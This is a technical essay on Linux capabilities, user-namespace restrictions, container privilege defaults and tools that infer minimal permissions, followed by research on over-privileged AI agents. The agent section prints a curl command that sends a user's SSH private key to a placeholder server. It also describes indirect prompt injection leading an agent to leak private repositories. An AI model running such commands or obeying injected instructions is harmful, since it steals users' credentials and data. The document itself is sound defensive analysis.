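In 2022 an administrator had only blunt ways to stop ordinary users from creating user namespaces. Lawler (2022), in *[PATCH 1/2] security, lsm* lists a limit on the number of namespaces, distribution-specific patches, and a kernel built without user namespaces. Frederick Lawler, of the network company Cloudflare, proposed a hook, a point at which the kernel calls security modules such as SELinux before it creates a user namespace. A module could then allow Chromium to create one and refuse an unknown program.

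Biederman (2022), in *[PATCH v5 0/4] Introduce security_create_user_ns()*, formally rejected the patch and complained that its supporters would not discuss the problems it was supposed to solve. He called it "an ineffective defense" and feared that it would break ordinary applications that rely on user namespaces. Paul Moore, who maintains the framework for security modules, replied that the hook it adds affects programs only if someone configures it to. Torvalds (2022) included Moore's explanation in the message merging the patch for Linux 6.1.

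Torvalds (2022), in *[GIT PULL] LSM patches for v6.1*, told Biederman that distributions were turning user namespaces off entirely. He personally thought it "was a mistake" to let users create them, but accepted that Linux was stuck with it. He also dismissed the existing limit on how many can be created. The limit stops someone from using up memory by creating thousands of namespaces, but one is enough to attack the kernel, and ordinary users need a few for sandboxes.

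The disagreement continued in May 2023, when Akihiro Suda proposed a setting that would allow only certain groups of users to create user namespaces. Moore suggested using the hook instead. Biederman answered that he had reported a real failure in Chromium caused by the hook, and asked whether any public SELinux policy used the hook. He also wrote that the hook could not technically reduce the attack surface.

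That last claim seems too strong. The hook only controls whether a program can create a user namespace. Denying a program keeps it from using a namespace to reach the kernel code behind it, but a program that is allowed to create one still receives every capability in it, even if its sandbox needs only one or two.

### Ubuntu's restriction

Ubuntu uses AppArmor to restrict both user namespaces and the capabilities that programs have inside them. AppArmor is a security module that can apply a set of rules, called a profile, to a program. Since version 24.04, an ordinary program without a profile can still create a user namespace, but AppArmor then moves it to a profile that denies it capabilities there. Programs known to need those capabilities, such as Chrome, have profiles that allow them.

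Calmels (2024), in *[PATCH 1/3] capabilities*, quotes John Johansen, who maintains AppArmor, on why it matters whether a program is refused a namespace or is later refused a capability. Programs built with QtWebEngine, a component for displaying web pages, crash if they cannot create a namespace, but cope well if they can create one and then lack a capability. Other programs cope better with being refused the namespace, and some crash either way.

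In March 2025 the security company Qualys published three ways around Ubuntu's restriction. An attacker could use a standard tool, `aa-exec`, to start a program under a permissive profile meant for a different one. The attacker could also use the shell in BusyBox, a collection of small utilities that had such a profile, or load a library into an allowed program with `LD_PRELOAD`. The last two have the same problem as attaching a capability to Python, because the administrator approves a program but its user decides what it runs. The restriction still blocks exploits that do not include one of these steps, and another Ubuntu setting blocks the `aa-exec` method.

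### A proposal for a sixth capability set

In May 2024 Jonathan Calmels proposed limiting the capabilities themselves. At present a new user namespace starts with a full set, even if its creator had a reduced bounding set outside. Calmels wanted to give each process another set, which would determine what it gets in any user namespace it creates:

```
new permitted = new effective = new bounding = namespace set
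```

The set would start full, so existing programs would work as before. A process could remove capabilities from it, and its children would inherit the reduced set. The set could never contain a capability missing from the process's bounding set. To add a capability back, a process would also need that capability in its permitted set, unless it had CAP_SETPCAP.

An administrator could then remove CAP_NET_ADMIN from the set for everyone who logs in remotely. Alice could still create a user namespace and run a sandbox in it, but she could not reach the firewall code that had caused three of the five vulnerabilities. A system-wide mask would do the same for every user. If a bug appeared in code that requires CAP_SYS_RAWIO, the administrator could set the mask to `0x1fffffdffff`, which turns on all 41 bits except the one for CAP_SYS_RAWIO.

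Casey Schaufler thought the capability calculation was already too complicated for most developers to tolerate, and he did not expect container developers to learn another set. Hallyn replied that an administrator could understand the new set without thinking about the others, and said that as a container developer himself he was "excited about it". Calmels quotes Schaufler as later accepting the aim but wanting the limit to be part of user namespaces, perhaps as an option when a process creates one.

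Such an option would be simpler, but every program that creates namespaces would have to use it. Calmels pointed out that changing all those programs was unrealistic, and that the service manager or login system needs to limit programs written by others. An attacker's program would not use the option. An inherited set does not depend on the program it restricts, which seems a good reason to accept the extra complexity.

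Biederman objected to part of the justification. Calmels had written that most distributions carried their own patches to control user namespaces or refused to enable them, and Biederman believed this had stopped long ago. Calmels replied by naming settings in kernels from Red Hat, Debian, Arch and Ubuntu. Both were partly right. The settings existed, but a distribution can have such a setting and still leave the feature on, and Debian had enabled unprivileged user namespaces by default in 2021.

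The second version, in June 2024, added a capability, CAP_SYS_CONTROL, to control changes to the mask. It also let security programs written in BPF change a process's capabilities when the process created a namespace. Moore rejected the BPF part because one security module would be changing data that belongs to another. A module might allow an action based on a process's capabilities, and a later module might then change them, so the result would depend on the order in which the modules ran. Hallyn approved the patch for the new set and suggested going ahead without the BPF part.

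The kernel does not seem to have adopted any of it. The Linux man-pages current in January 2026 list neither the set nor CAP_SYS_CONTROL, and a process that creates a user namespace still gets every capability there. Moore had recommended that people who wanted finer limits use a security module to control how processes use their capabilities. The Landlock patch proposed in May 2026 takes that approach. Until something like it is widely available, most administrators can control who may create a namespace but not what the namespace allows.

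### What Docker keeps

The kernel has no single object called a container. Docker, a widely used program for running containers, builds each one from several kinds of namespace, a reduced set of capabilities, a seccomp filter and other limits. By default it does not create a user namespace, so root in a Docker container has the machine's real user ID 0, and its capabilities count in system-wide checks.

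Docker gives such a container 14 of the 41 capabilities:

| Used for | Capabilities |
|---|---|
| Files | CAP_CHOWN, CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE, CAP_FOWNER, CAP_FSETID, CAP_MKNOD, CAP_SETFCAP |
| User IDs, groups and capability sets | CAP_SETUID, CAP_SETGID, CAP_SETPCAP |
| Networking | CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE, CAP_NET_RAW |
| Other tasks | CAP_KILL, CAP_SYS_CHROOT, CAP_AUDIT_WRITE |

Ten of the 14 capabilities are on Spengler's list of routes to root, but the container is much safer than that suggests because other mechanisms limit what a process can gain from most of those routes. CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE lets a process change any file it can see, but the mount namespace hides the host's files. CAP_SETUID lets it become user 0, but the bounding set keeps it from gaining the other 27 capabilities. CAP_MKNOD lets it create a device file for the host's disk, but a separate rule stops it from opening the device.

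Such a restriction fails if a capability offers a way past it. Early versions of Docker removed a list of dangerous capabilities and kept the rest, including CAP_DAC_READ_SEARCH. That capability also permits `open_by_handle_at`, a system call that opens a file by an identifying number instead of its path. In 2014 Sebastian Krahmer published a program that used this call inside a container to read the host's password file. The file had no path in the container, but it was on the same underlying file system. Docker now removes every capability and adds back 14, so it also excludes any capability that kernel developers add later.

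The network namespace makes two of the 14 capabilities less necessary. Since version 20.10, Docker has normally set the lowest unreserved port inside a container to 0, so a web server there can open port 443 without CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE. The setting affects only the container's own ports, which avoids the drawback it has on a shared machine. Docker also lets `ping` use the restricted kind of socket that Debian adopted, which doesn't need CAP_NET_RAW.

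### Privileged containers

The `--privileged` option gives a container all the capabilities and access to the host's devices. It also turns off the seccomp filter and the usual AppArmor or SELinux confinement. Because the container is normally in the initial user namespace, its CAP_SYS_ADMIN applies to the whole machine. An attacker inside the container can mount the host's disk, change the password file and log in to the host as root. People use this option for containers that manage hardware or run other containers, but it removes most of the protection that a container provides.

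The `--privileged` option grants less power in Docker's rootless mode, where Docker itself runs as an ordinary user inside a user namespace. A privileged container gets every capability, but only within that namespace, so it can't set the system clock, load a kernel module or open a disk that the user cannot open. A bug in the kernel code it can reach might still let an attacker escape.

Kubernetes publishes three security policies that an administrator can enforce. Under the strictest, called Restricted, every container must drop all capabilities and may add back only one:

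```
securityContext:
  capabilities:
    drop: ["ALL"]
    add: ["NET_BIND_SERVICE"]
```

The container must also run as a user other than root and use `no_new_privs`. The middle policy, Baseline, allows every capability in Docker's default set except CAP_NET_RAW. Neither policy applies unless an administrator turns it on. Without a policy, a container that specifies no capabilities gets the default set of the software that runs it, which is usually much the same as Docker's.

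Kubernetes can also run a container in its own user namespace. Since version 1.33, released in 2025, this needs no special cluster setting, but each application still has to request it with `hostUsers: false`. Root in the container then corresponds to an ordinary user on the host, so an attacker who escapes through a bug in the container software has neither root's user ID nor any capabilities there.

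### File capabilities for one namespace

Someone who installs `ping` in a container with its own user namespace may want to give the file CAP_NET_RAW. An ordinary file capability would be unsafe because it takes effect in any user namespace where the file runs. The container's root could attach every capability to a program, and an accomplice could then run it on the host with those capabilities. The kernel therefore used to prevent root in such a container from setting file capabilities.

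Since Linux 4.14, the kernel has let root in a container's user namespace set capabilities on files. It stores the user ID that this root has outside the container, such as 100000, with the file's capabilities. The file grants those capabilities only in a user namespace whose root has that outside ID, or in a descendant of such a namespace. `setcap` did not have to change, because the kernel adds the ID automatically.

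The mark identifies the container's root user, not the container itself. If two containers use the same range of IDs and share a file, a mark made in one also works in the other. An administrator who wants to keep containers fully apart should give each its own range.

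## Finding which capabilities a program needs

Docker gives every container the same 14 capabilities by default because its developers cannot know which program will run inside. An administrator who wants to grant fewer has to find out which ones the program needs.

### The smallest sufficient set

A set of capabilities is sufficient if the program can do all its expected work with that set. It is a smallest sufficient set if removing any one capability makes some of that work fail.

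The capabilities a program needs depend on how people use it. The version of `ping` that Criswell and colleagues studied needs CAP_NET_RAW to open its socket. It also needs CAP_NET_ADMIN if the user passes `-d`, which turns on debugging for the socket, or `-m`, which marks outgoing packets.

The capabilities a program needs also depend on its configuration. Spengler listed CAP_KILL, CAP_SETUID and CAP_SETGID for the Apache web server, which traditionally starts as root and runs its workers as another user. Sun, Song and colleagues (2022) report in *LiCA* that Apache needs only CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE when an ordinary user starts it. A web server that receives its socket from systemd needs no capabilities.

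A program can also have two smallest sets of capabilities that differ greatly in power. The kernel accepts either CAP_PERFMON or CAP_SYS_ADMIN for performance monitoring, so either is enough for a tool that does nothing else. Both sets have one member, but CAP_SYS_ADMIN is root-equivalent.

The kernel sometimes checks for a capability that the program can do without. Sun and colleagues give the example of `open`, the system call for opening a file. When the kernel's quick count of open files reaches the system-wide limit, it checks whether the process has CAP_SYS_ADMIN. If the process lacks it, the kernel counts again more exactly and refuses to open the file only if that count has also reached the limit. Almost every program opens files, so anyone who granted every capability the kernel might check for would give CAP_SYS_ADMIN to almost every program.

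### Three methods on a small daemon

Suppose that a small daemon keeps a machine's clock right and tells other machines the time. It runs as an ordinary user and does four things:

- It opens port 123, which requires CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE.
- It reads its settings and writes a log, using files that its own user owns. This requires no capability.
- It gives its network packets a priority, which it reads from its settings. In Linux 5.4, the version that Sun and colleagues analysed, priorities from 0 to 6 require no capability and others require CAP_NET_ADMIN. This daemon uses 3.
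- It corrects the clock when the time is wrong, which requires CAP_SYS_TIME.

The daemon therefore needs only CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE and CAP_SYS_TIME. The administrator, who doesn't know this, tests the daemon for an hour while the clock happens to be right.

She could start the daemon without capabilities and watch for refused system calls. The tool `strace` prints each call a program makes and its result. Edge shows that searching this output for the error EPERM reveals that `ping` cannot open its socket. The same search would find nothing here, because Linux returns EACCES instead when a process isn't allowed to open a reserved port. If she searches for both errors, she finds the failure, grants CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE and restarts the daemon. The second run produces no errors, so she doesn't learn that the daemon also needs CAP_SYS_TIME until the clock drifts and the daemon fails to correct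 it.

The error also doesn't show which capability is missing, and granting one may be the wrong fix. If the log belonged to another user, CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE would let the daemon write to it and to every other file on the machine. Changing the log's owner would be much safer. Edge advises administrators to check that each capability is reasonable for the program's task before granting it.

The `capable` tool traces the kernel's capability checks and prints the name of each capability checked while a program runs. The administrator can give the daemon every capability during the test so it does not stop at the first refusal. She should still run it as its ordinary user, because root can open its own files without CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE, and the trace would miss any need for it. The trace shows CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE but not CAP_SYS_TIME, because the daemon never corrected the clock during the test.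 If the machine reached its limit on open files during the test, the trace also shows CAP_SYS_ADMIN.

Static analysis examines the program's code without running it. The analyst lists the system calls that the program could make, then looks up which capabilities the kernel might check for each. This finds the call that corrects the clock, but the list that Hasan and colleagues published links the daemon's five relevant calls (`socket`, `bind`, `setsockopt`, `open` and `clock_adjtime`) to nine capabilities. It links `bind` to CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE and `open` to CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE, regardless of which port the program binds or who owns the file.

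| Method | Needed capabilities found | Unneeded capabilities reported |
|---|---|---|
| Watching for refused calls | CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE | None |
| Tracing the kernel's checks | CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE | Possibly CAP_SYS_ADMIN |
| Looking up system calls in the published list | CAP_NET_BIND_SERVICE, CAP_SYS_TIME | Seven, including CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE and CAP_NET_ADMIN |

An analyst can judge more precisely which capabilities a program needs by considering the arguments it passes to each system call, though this doesn't settle every case. For example, if the program reads a socket's priority from a settings file, the administrator may later change it to a value that requires CAP_NET_ADMIN, so a cautious analyst would keep that capability.

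Static analysis can also miss capabilities that a program needs. A program may choose which function to call at run time, and the analyst may not identify all the possibilities. Any helper programs that the daemon starts need their own analysis.

### The 2022 tools

Hasan and colleagues tried to reduce the over-counting in two ways. They ran two existing tools that list a program's system calls and kept only the calls on both lists. For `chfn`, which changes a user's personal details, one tool had included `mount` only because a library that `chfn` loads contains code for it. They also checked the arguments of 12 of the 28 system calls linked to CAP_SYS_ADMIN.

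Half of the 201 setuid programs tested needed fewer than 16 of the test kernel's 38 capabilities. The results ranged from seven to 27. The researchers observed no failures with the reduced sets, and they checked the source code of eight programs by hand to confirm that the discarded system calls were unnecessary. The tool still over-counted considerably. It gives `ping` 16 capabilities, based on 50 system calls, according to the *Decap Step by Step Guide*.

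Sun and colleagues focused on the conditions under which the kernel checks for a capability. Their tool traces the code back from each check to a system call and calculates which arguments lead to the check, with results for 428 system calls. To find out which calls a program makes, they ran it on sample commands, randomly altering each command 10,000 times. They analysed the program's own code only if the result differed from the developer's list of capabilities.

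This procedure would miss a capability that the developer overlooked and the test runs did not reveal. That may have happened with `ping`. Sun and colleagues report only CAP_NET_RAW, although their analysis of the kernel shows that the settings used by `-d` and `-m` lead to a check for CAP_NET_ADMIN. They may have used a different version of `ping` from Criswell and colleagues, or not counted a refused option as a failure.

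One study examined 114 programs and found problems with eight. Three requested too many capabilities, three requested root, one came with no instructions, and one had different settings in different projects. Such problems are probably more common in software generally, because most of the programs studied came from developers who already used capabilities.

The clearest case of excess privilege was netsniff-ng, a set of eight networking tools. Its installation instructions granted all eight the same four capabilities, including CAP_SYS_ADMIN, but only one tool needed all four and one needed none. Altogether, the tools needed 14 of the 32 capabilities granted.

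To check whether their tool reported unnecessary capabilities, Sun and colleagues removed each reported capability in turn and ran the program again. Every removal caused an error, so they concluded that all of them were necessary. This test cannot find capabilities that the tool missed. The researchers estimated that it missed fewer than 8% of capabilities, because their method for tracing indirect function calls in the kernel finds over 92% of those calls. The estimate does not follow, since missing a single call might cause the tool to miss a capability that many programs need, or none at all.

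Later researchers have looked beyond individual programs. *CapAssess* proposes three tools for diagnosing problems in how capabilities are designed, how the kernel enforces them and how programs use them.

### KubeCap

Containers add another difficulty, because the developer sets their capabilities in a configuration file that is separate from the program. *KubeCap* describes a tool that compares the two for programs written in the language Go. It works in five steps:

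1. It fills in the project's configuration templates to produce a manifest, the file that tells Kubernetes how to run a container. From this it reads the container's capabilities.
2. It finds the program that the container actually starts, looking past any scripts that launch it, and locates the source code.
3. It follows the function calls from the start of the program and lists the system calls that the program could reach.
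4. It finds the capability checks in the kernel's source code and traces each one back towards a system call. It gives this code to GPT-4o-mini, a small language model that OpenAI released in 2024. The model writes a rule naming the system call, the argument, the condition and the capability.
5. It works out the arguments in the program where it can, and applies the rules to infer which capabilities the program needs.

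For example, one rule is that `fcntl` may require CAP_SYS_RESOURCE when a program uses it to enlarge a pipe beyond the normal limit. Hasan and colleagues had worked out their conditions by hand, and only for CAP_SYS_ADMIN.

The language model is not used in the other steps, but a wrong rule could make the tool remove a necessary capability or keep an unnecessary one. The researchers inspected 97 conditional rules and judged 77 (79%) valid. They could apply 64 without approximation. They say people verify the model's output before the tool uses it, so a reviewer would have to catch the invalid rules, about one in five.

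The tool then calculates the excess:

```
excess = capabilities in the manifest − inferred capabilities
```

The web application podinfo originally had the default 14 capabilities. Ten of these, or 71%, were excess because they were not in the inferred set. The tool writes a new manifest that drops every capability and adds back the inferred set.

The researchers tested ten workloads, with one container from each:

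| Workload | Original capabilities | Removed | Left |
|---|---|---|---|
| podinfo, ced | 14 | 10 | 4 |
| twitter-go | 14 | 7 | 7 |
| deckhouse, gardener-extension-cri-resmgr, minibroker, poolprovider-for-k8s | 14 | 6 | 8 |
| amazon-vpc-cni-k8s, eks-anywhere | 2 | 1 | 1 |
| Intel-ECI-ExCat-K8s | 41 | 35 | 6 |

The average reduction in capabilities was 55%, but it depended heavily on how the researchers traced function calls. Go programs often call a function through an interface with several implementations. An analysis that assumed any of these implementations might run removed only one capability from podinfo and an average of 8% across the ten workloads. A stricter method removed six from podinfo and an average of 38% across the workloads.

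Removing more is an improvement only if the program still works, because an analysis that missed necessary calls would also remove more. The researchers report functional tests for four of the ten workloads, of which podinfo, minibroker and ced passed.

The fourth was amazon-vpc-cni-k8s, which connects containers to Amazon's network. Its main container kept working without CAP_NET_RAW but failed without CAP_NET_ADMIN. A second container, the node agent, seemed to work without CAP_NET_ADMIN. However, the test checked whether two applications could still reach each other, which does not show that the agent could still do its job of blocking forbidden traffic.

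The main container also crashed without the `privileged` setting, so the researchers left it on. A privileged container normally has every capability, whatever its manifest lists. If the setting applied to the container they tested, removing CAP_NET_RAW from the list probably had no effect. They counted this container as having two capabilities, but counted the privileged Intel container as having all 41.

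The figures for ced suggest another problem. The tool removed ten of ced's 14 capabilities, leaving four, but *KubeCap* also reports that the inferred set had eight. Both numbers can be right if four of the inferred capabilities were not in the original set. The stricter of the two alternative methods inferred 15 capabilities for ced, more than the original 14, which supports this explanation. If it is correct, the new manifest would give ced four capabilities it did not have before, and the formula for the excess would not count them. *KubeCap* gives only the number of capabilities, so readers cannot tell which ones these were.

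The researchers did not run the 2022 tools on the same workloads, so it is unclear whether their own tool is more accurate. It does cover Kubernetes configuration that the earlier tools did not handle.

### When the smallest set is still as good as root

A percentage reduction counts every capability equally. Hasan and colleagues achieved their largest reduction, 82%, by cutting the program `hashquery` from 38 capabilities to seven. One of the seven was CAP_DAC_OVERRIDE, which the tool left in all 201 programs. As long as `hashquery` has it, removing the others gives little protection against an attacker who can run arbitrary code.

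The KubeCap results have the same weakness. Ten of the 14 default capabilities are on Spengler's list, so a container that keeps eight of the 14 still has at least four from his list, and twitter-go still has at least three. Of the seven containers that started with the default set, only podinfo and ced could have lost all ten. The container's other restrictions, rather than the smaller capability set, block most of these routes to the host.

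The reduction matters much more for netsniff-ng, because seven of the eight tools can run without CAP_SYS_ADMIN and none of the capabilities they keep is among Spengler's 19. However, CAP_NET_ADMIN and CAP_NET_RAW are on his separate list of likely routes to full root.

Removing a less powerful capability can also stop a process from reaching faulty kernel code. CVE-2020-14386, for example, was a bug in the kernel's packet sockets, and a process needed CAP_NET_RAW to create such a socket. A container without that capability was safe from attacks on this bug even if it kept several others.

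Criswell and colleagues measured what an attacker could do with a program's remaining capabilities, and for how much of its run. Their method first removes each capability once the program can no longer use it. This was not enough for `su`, which kept CAP_SETUID for 88% of its run because it switches to the other user near the end. They rewrote `su` to store the other user's ID as its saved user ID at the start, so it could give up CAP_SETUID early and still switch later.

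They report that the new `su` was vulnerable for only about 1% of its run. But for another 87%, their program's search for ways to read or write the machine's memory did not finish within five hours. They counted this part as safe because the search usually finds an attack quickly when one exists. The program proved `su` safe from all four modelled attacks for only 12% of the run.

The percentages also depend on the test. The small web server executed 90% of its instructions without capabilities in a test where it delivered one file. Delivering more files would have raised that share without making the server safer. A bug in the code that reads requests from strangers is also more likely to be exploited than one in the startup code, regardless of how many instructions each part executes.

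A more direct test would be to attack programs with known exploits before and after reducing their capabilities, and record what the attacker gains. *KubeCap* cites a 2018 study in which Lin and colleagues ran real exploits inside containers and found that many still worked under the default settings. There seems to be no comparable test of containers or programs that have only the capabilities they need.

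## Broad permissions in AI agents

Researchers can estimate which capabilities a program needs because its code is fixed before it runs. With an AI agent, the user describes a task in ordinary language, and a language model decides step by step what to do. Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues (2025), in *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing*, give the example of an agent that has to comment on issue 745 in GitLab, a service for managing software projects. It needs to open that issue and write in its comment box. If the user then asks for a summary of the issue, the agent no longer needs to write in GitLab. Nobody can know which permissions each task will need when setting up the agent, and *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) warns that developers are tempted to give agents broad tools and credentials from the start.

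An agent has excessive permissions if people grant it more than its task requires. This is different from using a powerful tool when a weaker one would do, and from taking an action that damages or discloses something. An agent may never misuse its excess permissions, and one with only the permissions it needs can still delete the wrong file.

### Tools, credentials and approvals

A language model only produces text. The program that runs it, often called a harness, gives it a list of tools, each with a name and description. To use a tool, the model writes the tool's name and arguments, such as a file to open. The harness runs the tool and adds the result to the model's input. The model and harness repeat this until the task is finished.

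Many of an agent's tools act on an outside service and need a credential, such as an access token, to do so. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) describes a coding assistant connected to GitHub, where developers store and share code. The user gives it an older type of token that covers every repository she can access. The assistant can then use about 40 tools in all of those repositories, including 16 that can make changes. To summarise the open issues of one repository, it needs only two read-only tools and access to that repository.

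Hiding the other tools from the model would not reduce the token's permissions. If the assistant also had a tool for sending arbitrary web requests, it could use the same token to do what the hidden tools do. Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa therefore define an agent's effective authority as everything it can cause to happen through any credential or tool available to it.

Like Linux capabilities, credentials tend to cover kinds of operation rather than specific operations. OAuth is a common standard for giving one application access to an account on another service. Sharma, Jiang and colleagues point out in *PAuth* that a user can use OAuth to let an agent transfer money, but not to limit the agent to transferring $100 to Bob.

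Finally, the harness may ask a person for approval before it runs a tool. Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, originally asked by default before every file change and shell command, according to the company's *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026). Users can write rules that approve certain commands in advance.

### Three catch-all grants

A shell gives an agent access to every command-line program on the machine, including any installed later. *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture* (2026) notes that coding agents open shells and network connections under their user's identity.

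Suppose that Alice's agent has a `read_file` tool that opens only files in her project, and a `send_request` tool that asks for her approval before contacting a server. She also lets it run shell commands without asking. The agent can now run this command:

```
curl --data-binary @$HOME/.ssh/id_ed25519 $SERVER
```

`curl` reads the private key that Alice uses for remote logins and sends it to the server named in `$SERVER`. The agent has used neither `read_file` nor `send_request`, so the restrictions on them do not apply. The kernel allows the command because the shell runs under Alice's user ID, and she may read her own key and open network connections. The shell needs none of the 41 capabilities for this, so removing them all would not prevent it.

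The model might run such a command because of text an attacker has placed in a file. *Authority Is Not a String* (2026) describes this problem, known as indirect prompt injection, in which any text a coding agent reads in project files, comments or tool output can act as an instruction.

Alice's separate permissions would matter again if she confined the shell. She could run it in a container that does not contain her key, or block its connections to unapproved servers. The kernel would then apply the limits to `curl` and every other program the shell starts. *Permission Denied* (2026) tests coding agents under such restrictions. One of its policies allows connections only to listed servers, makes most of the file system read-only and removes special privileges. A read-only file system would still let `curl` read Alice's key, so the network restriction would have to stop the theft.

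An access token for a whole account is another catch-all. Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa cite a May 2025 report from the security company Invariant Labs, in which a malicious instruction in a public repository led an agent to read its user's private repositories and publish their contents. A token that allowed only reading the public repository would have prevented this. But the user's later tasks might require permission to write, for example to fix a program, or access to another repository.

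An administrator-level tool can change data or settings without the usual checks. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes an internal case where someone asked Claude to set up read-only access to billing information. Claude instead chose a role with full administrative control of the cloud account, and an automated check blocked the action.

Users also create catch-alls through their approval rules. Anthropic reports that in June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule approving some shell commands in advance. It says 5% allowed every shell command and another 43% had rules approving interpreters such as Python, which can run any command. These may be percentages of all active users or only of those with rules, so the share of active users who had in effect approved everything was either about 48% or about 24%.

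A rule that lets an agent run Python is as broad as one that lets it use the whole shell, because a Python script can start any other program. Treating the Python rule as narrower repeats the mistake of the administrator who attached a capability to the Python interpreter.

### How much people and models grant

Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa write that 99.8% of 447,000 GitHub workflows were over-privileged. Workflows are automated scripts rather than AI agents. GitHub runs them, for example, to test each change to a program. The figure comes from *Characterizing the Security of GitHub CI Workflows*, which Igibek Koishybayev and colleagues presented at the USENIX Security conference in 2022. They found that the over-privileged workflows could write to their repositories instead of only reading them.

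At that time GitHub normally gave workflows write access unless someone restricted it, so the figure mostly reflects how rarely people changed the default. Similarly, most of the Kubernetes projects surveyed for *KubeCap* left their containers' capabilities unset. In February 2023 GitHub made read-only access the default for new organisations and for new repositories in personal accounts, but did not change existing settings. A new count would probably give a lower figure.

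Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa also cite a 2023 Microsoft analysis, which found that accounts on several cloud services used only 1% of their permissions. The other 99% were probably not all excessive, because an unused permission may still be necessary, as CAP_SYS_TIME was for the clock daemon.

A language model could instead write the permissions for each task. *Do Coding Agents Understand Least-Privilege Authorization?* (Yan, Weng and colleagues, 2026) tested this on 120 realistic command-line tasks. For each task, a model had to list the files an agent could read, write or execute. People had reviewed the correct answers, and programs checked whether the task could still be completed and whether attacks succeeded under the model's list.

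Leading models often left out access that the task required and granted access that it did not use, some of it to sensitive files. Models given more time to reason still made these errors, but each became more consistent in either granting too much access or granting too little.

Results improved when the researchers split the work into two steps. The model first imagined carrying out the task and listed everything it might need, then checked each item. For models that had been too strict, success on tasks involving sensitive files rose by up to 15.8%. Attacks succeeded less often with every model tested.

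*Aletheia* (2026) checks the permissions requested in a project's instruction file by running a coding agent with all of them, then removing one and running the agent again. Sun and colleagues tested Linux capabilities in much the same way.

The method's results are harder to interpret when permissions overlap. *Aletheia* points out that removing permission to read a file may have no effect if another permission gives access to the same directory. Each of the two would then look unnecessary, although the agent needs one of them. If the agent has an unconfined shell, nearly every other permission might look unnecessary, because the agent could do the same work through the shell.

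### Choosing a stronger tool than necessary

In *When Lower Privileges Suffice*, Yang, Bu and colleagues (2026) tested how agents choose between tools when several would work. In one scenario, a user asks an agent to enrol a student in a biology course. Three tools do this through the university's normal procedures, while three stronger ones bypass them, for example by forcing the enrolment as an administrator or writing directly to the database.

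The study has 544 such scenarios, in areas including business, healthcare and computer infrastructure. Each offers three weaker and three stronger tools, any of which can complete the task alone. Two language models and human reviewers checked that each tool was sufficient, so that an agent would have no good reason to prefer a stronger one.

All the tools were simulated. The first call to each weaker tool failed with a temporary error, such as the service being briefly unreachable, and later calls succeeded. The stronger tools always worked. An agent had up to five turns, and the researchers counted its behaviour as over-privileged if it used a stronger tool before trying all three weaker ones.

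Six of the 11 models did this in more than 30% of scenarios. The rate was 64.9% for Qwen3-8B, a small model that anyone can download, and below 10% for GPT-5.2, GLM-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.6. Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa therefore quote the result correctly but leave out the scripted failures, which account for much of it.

GPT-5.2, for example, chose a stronger tool first in only five scenarios. It switched to a stronger tool after trying one weaker tool in 13 scenarios, and after trying two in 35. The researchers suggest that repeated errors lead models to treat the weaker tools as unreliable, though the experiment doesn't show why the models switched.

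Training two small models to refuse harmful requests, using an existing safety training method, did not reliably reduce over-privileged tool use. One model's score on a test of harmful behaviour fell from 41.9% to 6.7%, but its rate of over-privileged tool use rose from 50.4% to 60.7%. The other model's harmful behaviour score fell from 67.4% to 10.5%, but its rate of over-privileged tool use fell only from 68.8% to 62.5%. A model that has learned to refuse harmful requests has not necessarily learned which tool to use for a legitimate one, such as enrolling a student.

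Instructing models to use the least powerful tool and to retry after a failure reduced the problem, but helped less once tools had failed. Training models on tool choice worked better. The researchers showed them examples of good choices, then rewarded them in simulated scenarios for finishing with the weaker tools. This cut Qwen3-8B's rate from 64.9% to 27.0% and hardly changed its scores on general tests.

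Some of that improvement may only be a delay in using stronger tools. The training also gave a small reward to a model that tried every weaker tool once and then used a stronger one. The study's main measure does not count this as over-privileged, even though each weaker tool would have worked on a second attempt.

### Labelling the tools

Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues (2026), in *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?*, measured this kind of delay. In October 2026 they ran the same 544 scenarios on eight models with a label added to each tool's description, with Yang and colleagues' instruction, with both, and with neither. A typical label was `[Privilege: administer, cost 9/10]`.

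The results for Qwen3.5-397B, a large model, show why the choice of measure matters:

| What the model received | Used a stronger tool before trying all the weaker ones | Used a stronger tool at any point | Finished without a stronger tool |
|---|---|---|---|
| Neither | 38.4% | 77.2% | 18.8% |
| Labels | 19.1% | 73.0% | 21.5% |
| Instruction | 9.9% | 53.5% | 39.5% |
| Both | 2.9% | 39.3% | 51.1% |

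Labels halved the rate on Yang and colleagues' measure, but the model still used a stronger tool at some point in nearly as many scenarios as before, usually after trying the weaker ones. In one scenario, it called all three weaker tools, got an error from each and then used the stronger one. With both the labels and the instruction, it retried the first weaker tool, and the call succeeded.

Without labels or the instruction, five of the eight models used a stronger tool at some point in more than 60% of scenarios. The earlier study's figures therefore understate how often agents used power they did not need, at least when every weaker tool fails once.

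Tool failures had the clearest effect on two smaller Qwen models, which the researchers also tested with all tools working from the start. The models used a stronger tool in 8.1% and 6.1% of scenarios when all tools worked, and in 70.4% and 87.7% when tools failed.

The content of the labels mattered. Replacing them with a note about each tool's typical response time did not significantly improve any model, and it made DeepSeek-v3.2 more likely to choose a stronger tool too early. In a smaller test on two models, however, most of the labels' benefit remained when 30% of the costs were random. An attacker who could change the labels might therefore be able to steer an agent towards a powerful tool.

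A low rate of over-privileged choices can also mean that an agent did not finish its work. Claude Sonnet 4.6 completed only 19.9% of the tasks without any help, because it usually tried each weaker tool once, then stopped and reported the errors. This might be reasonable in a real system, since the user could decide what to do next. With labels, Llama-3.1-8B often called tools that did not exist, and its completion rate fell from 82.0% to 45.2%.

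Results for the same model can vary widely between experiments. Yang and colleagues reported a rate of 55.9% for Llama-3.1-8B, but Parkinson and colleagues measured 12.9%. The results for GPT-5.2, Claude and Kimi K2.5 were much closer. Each condition was run only once, and the labels separated the weaker and stronger tools perfectly, which might not happen in a real system.

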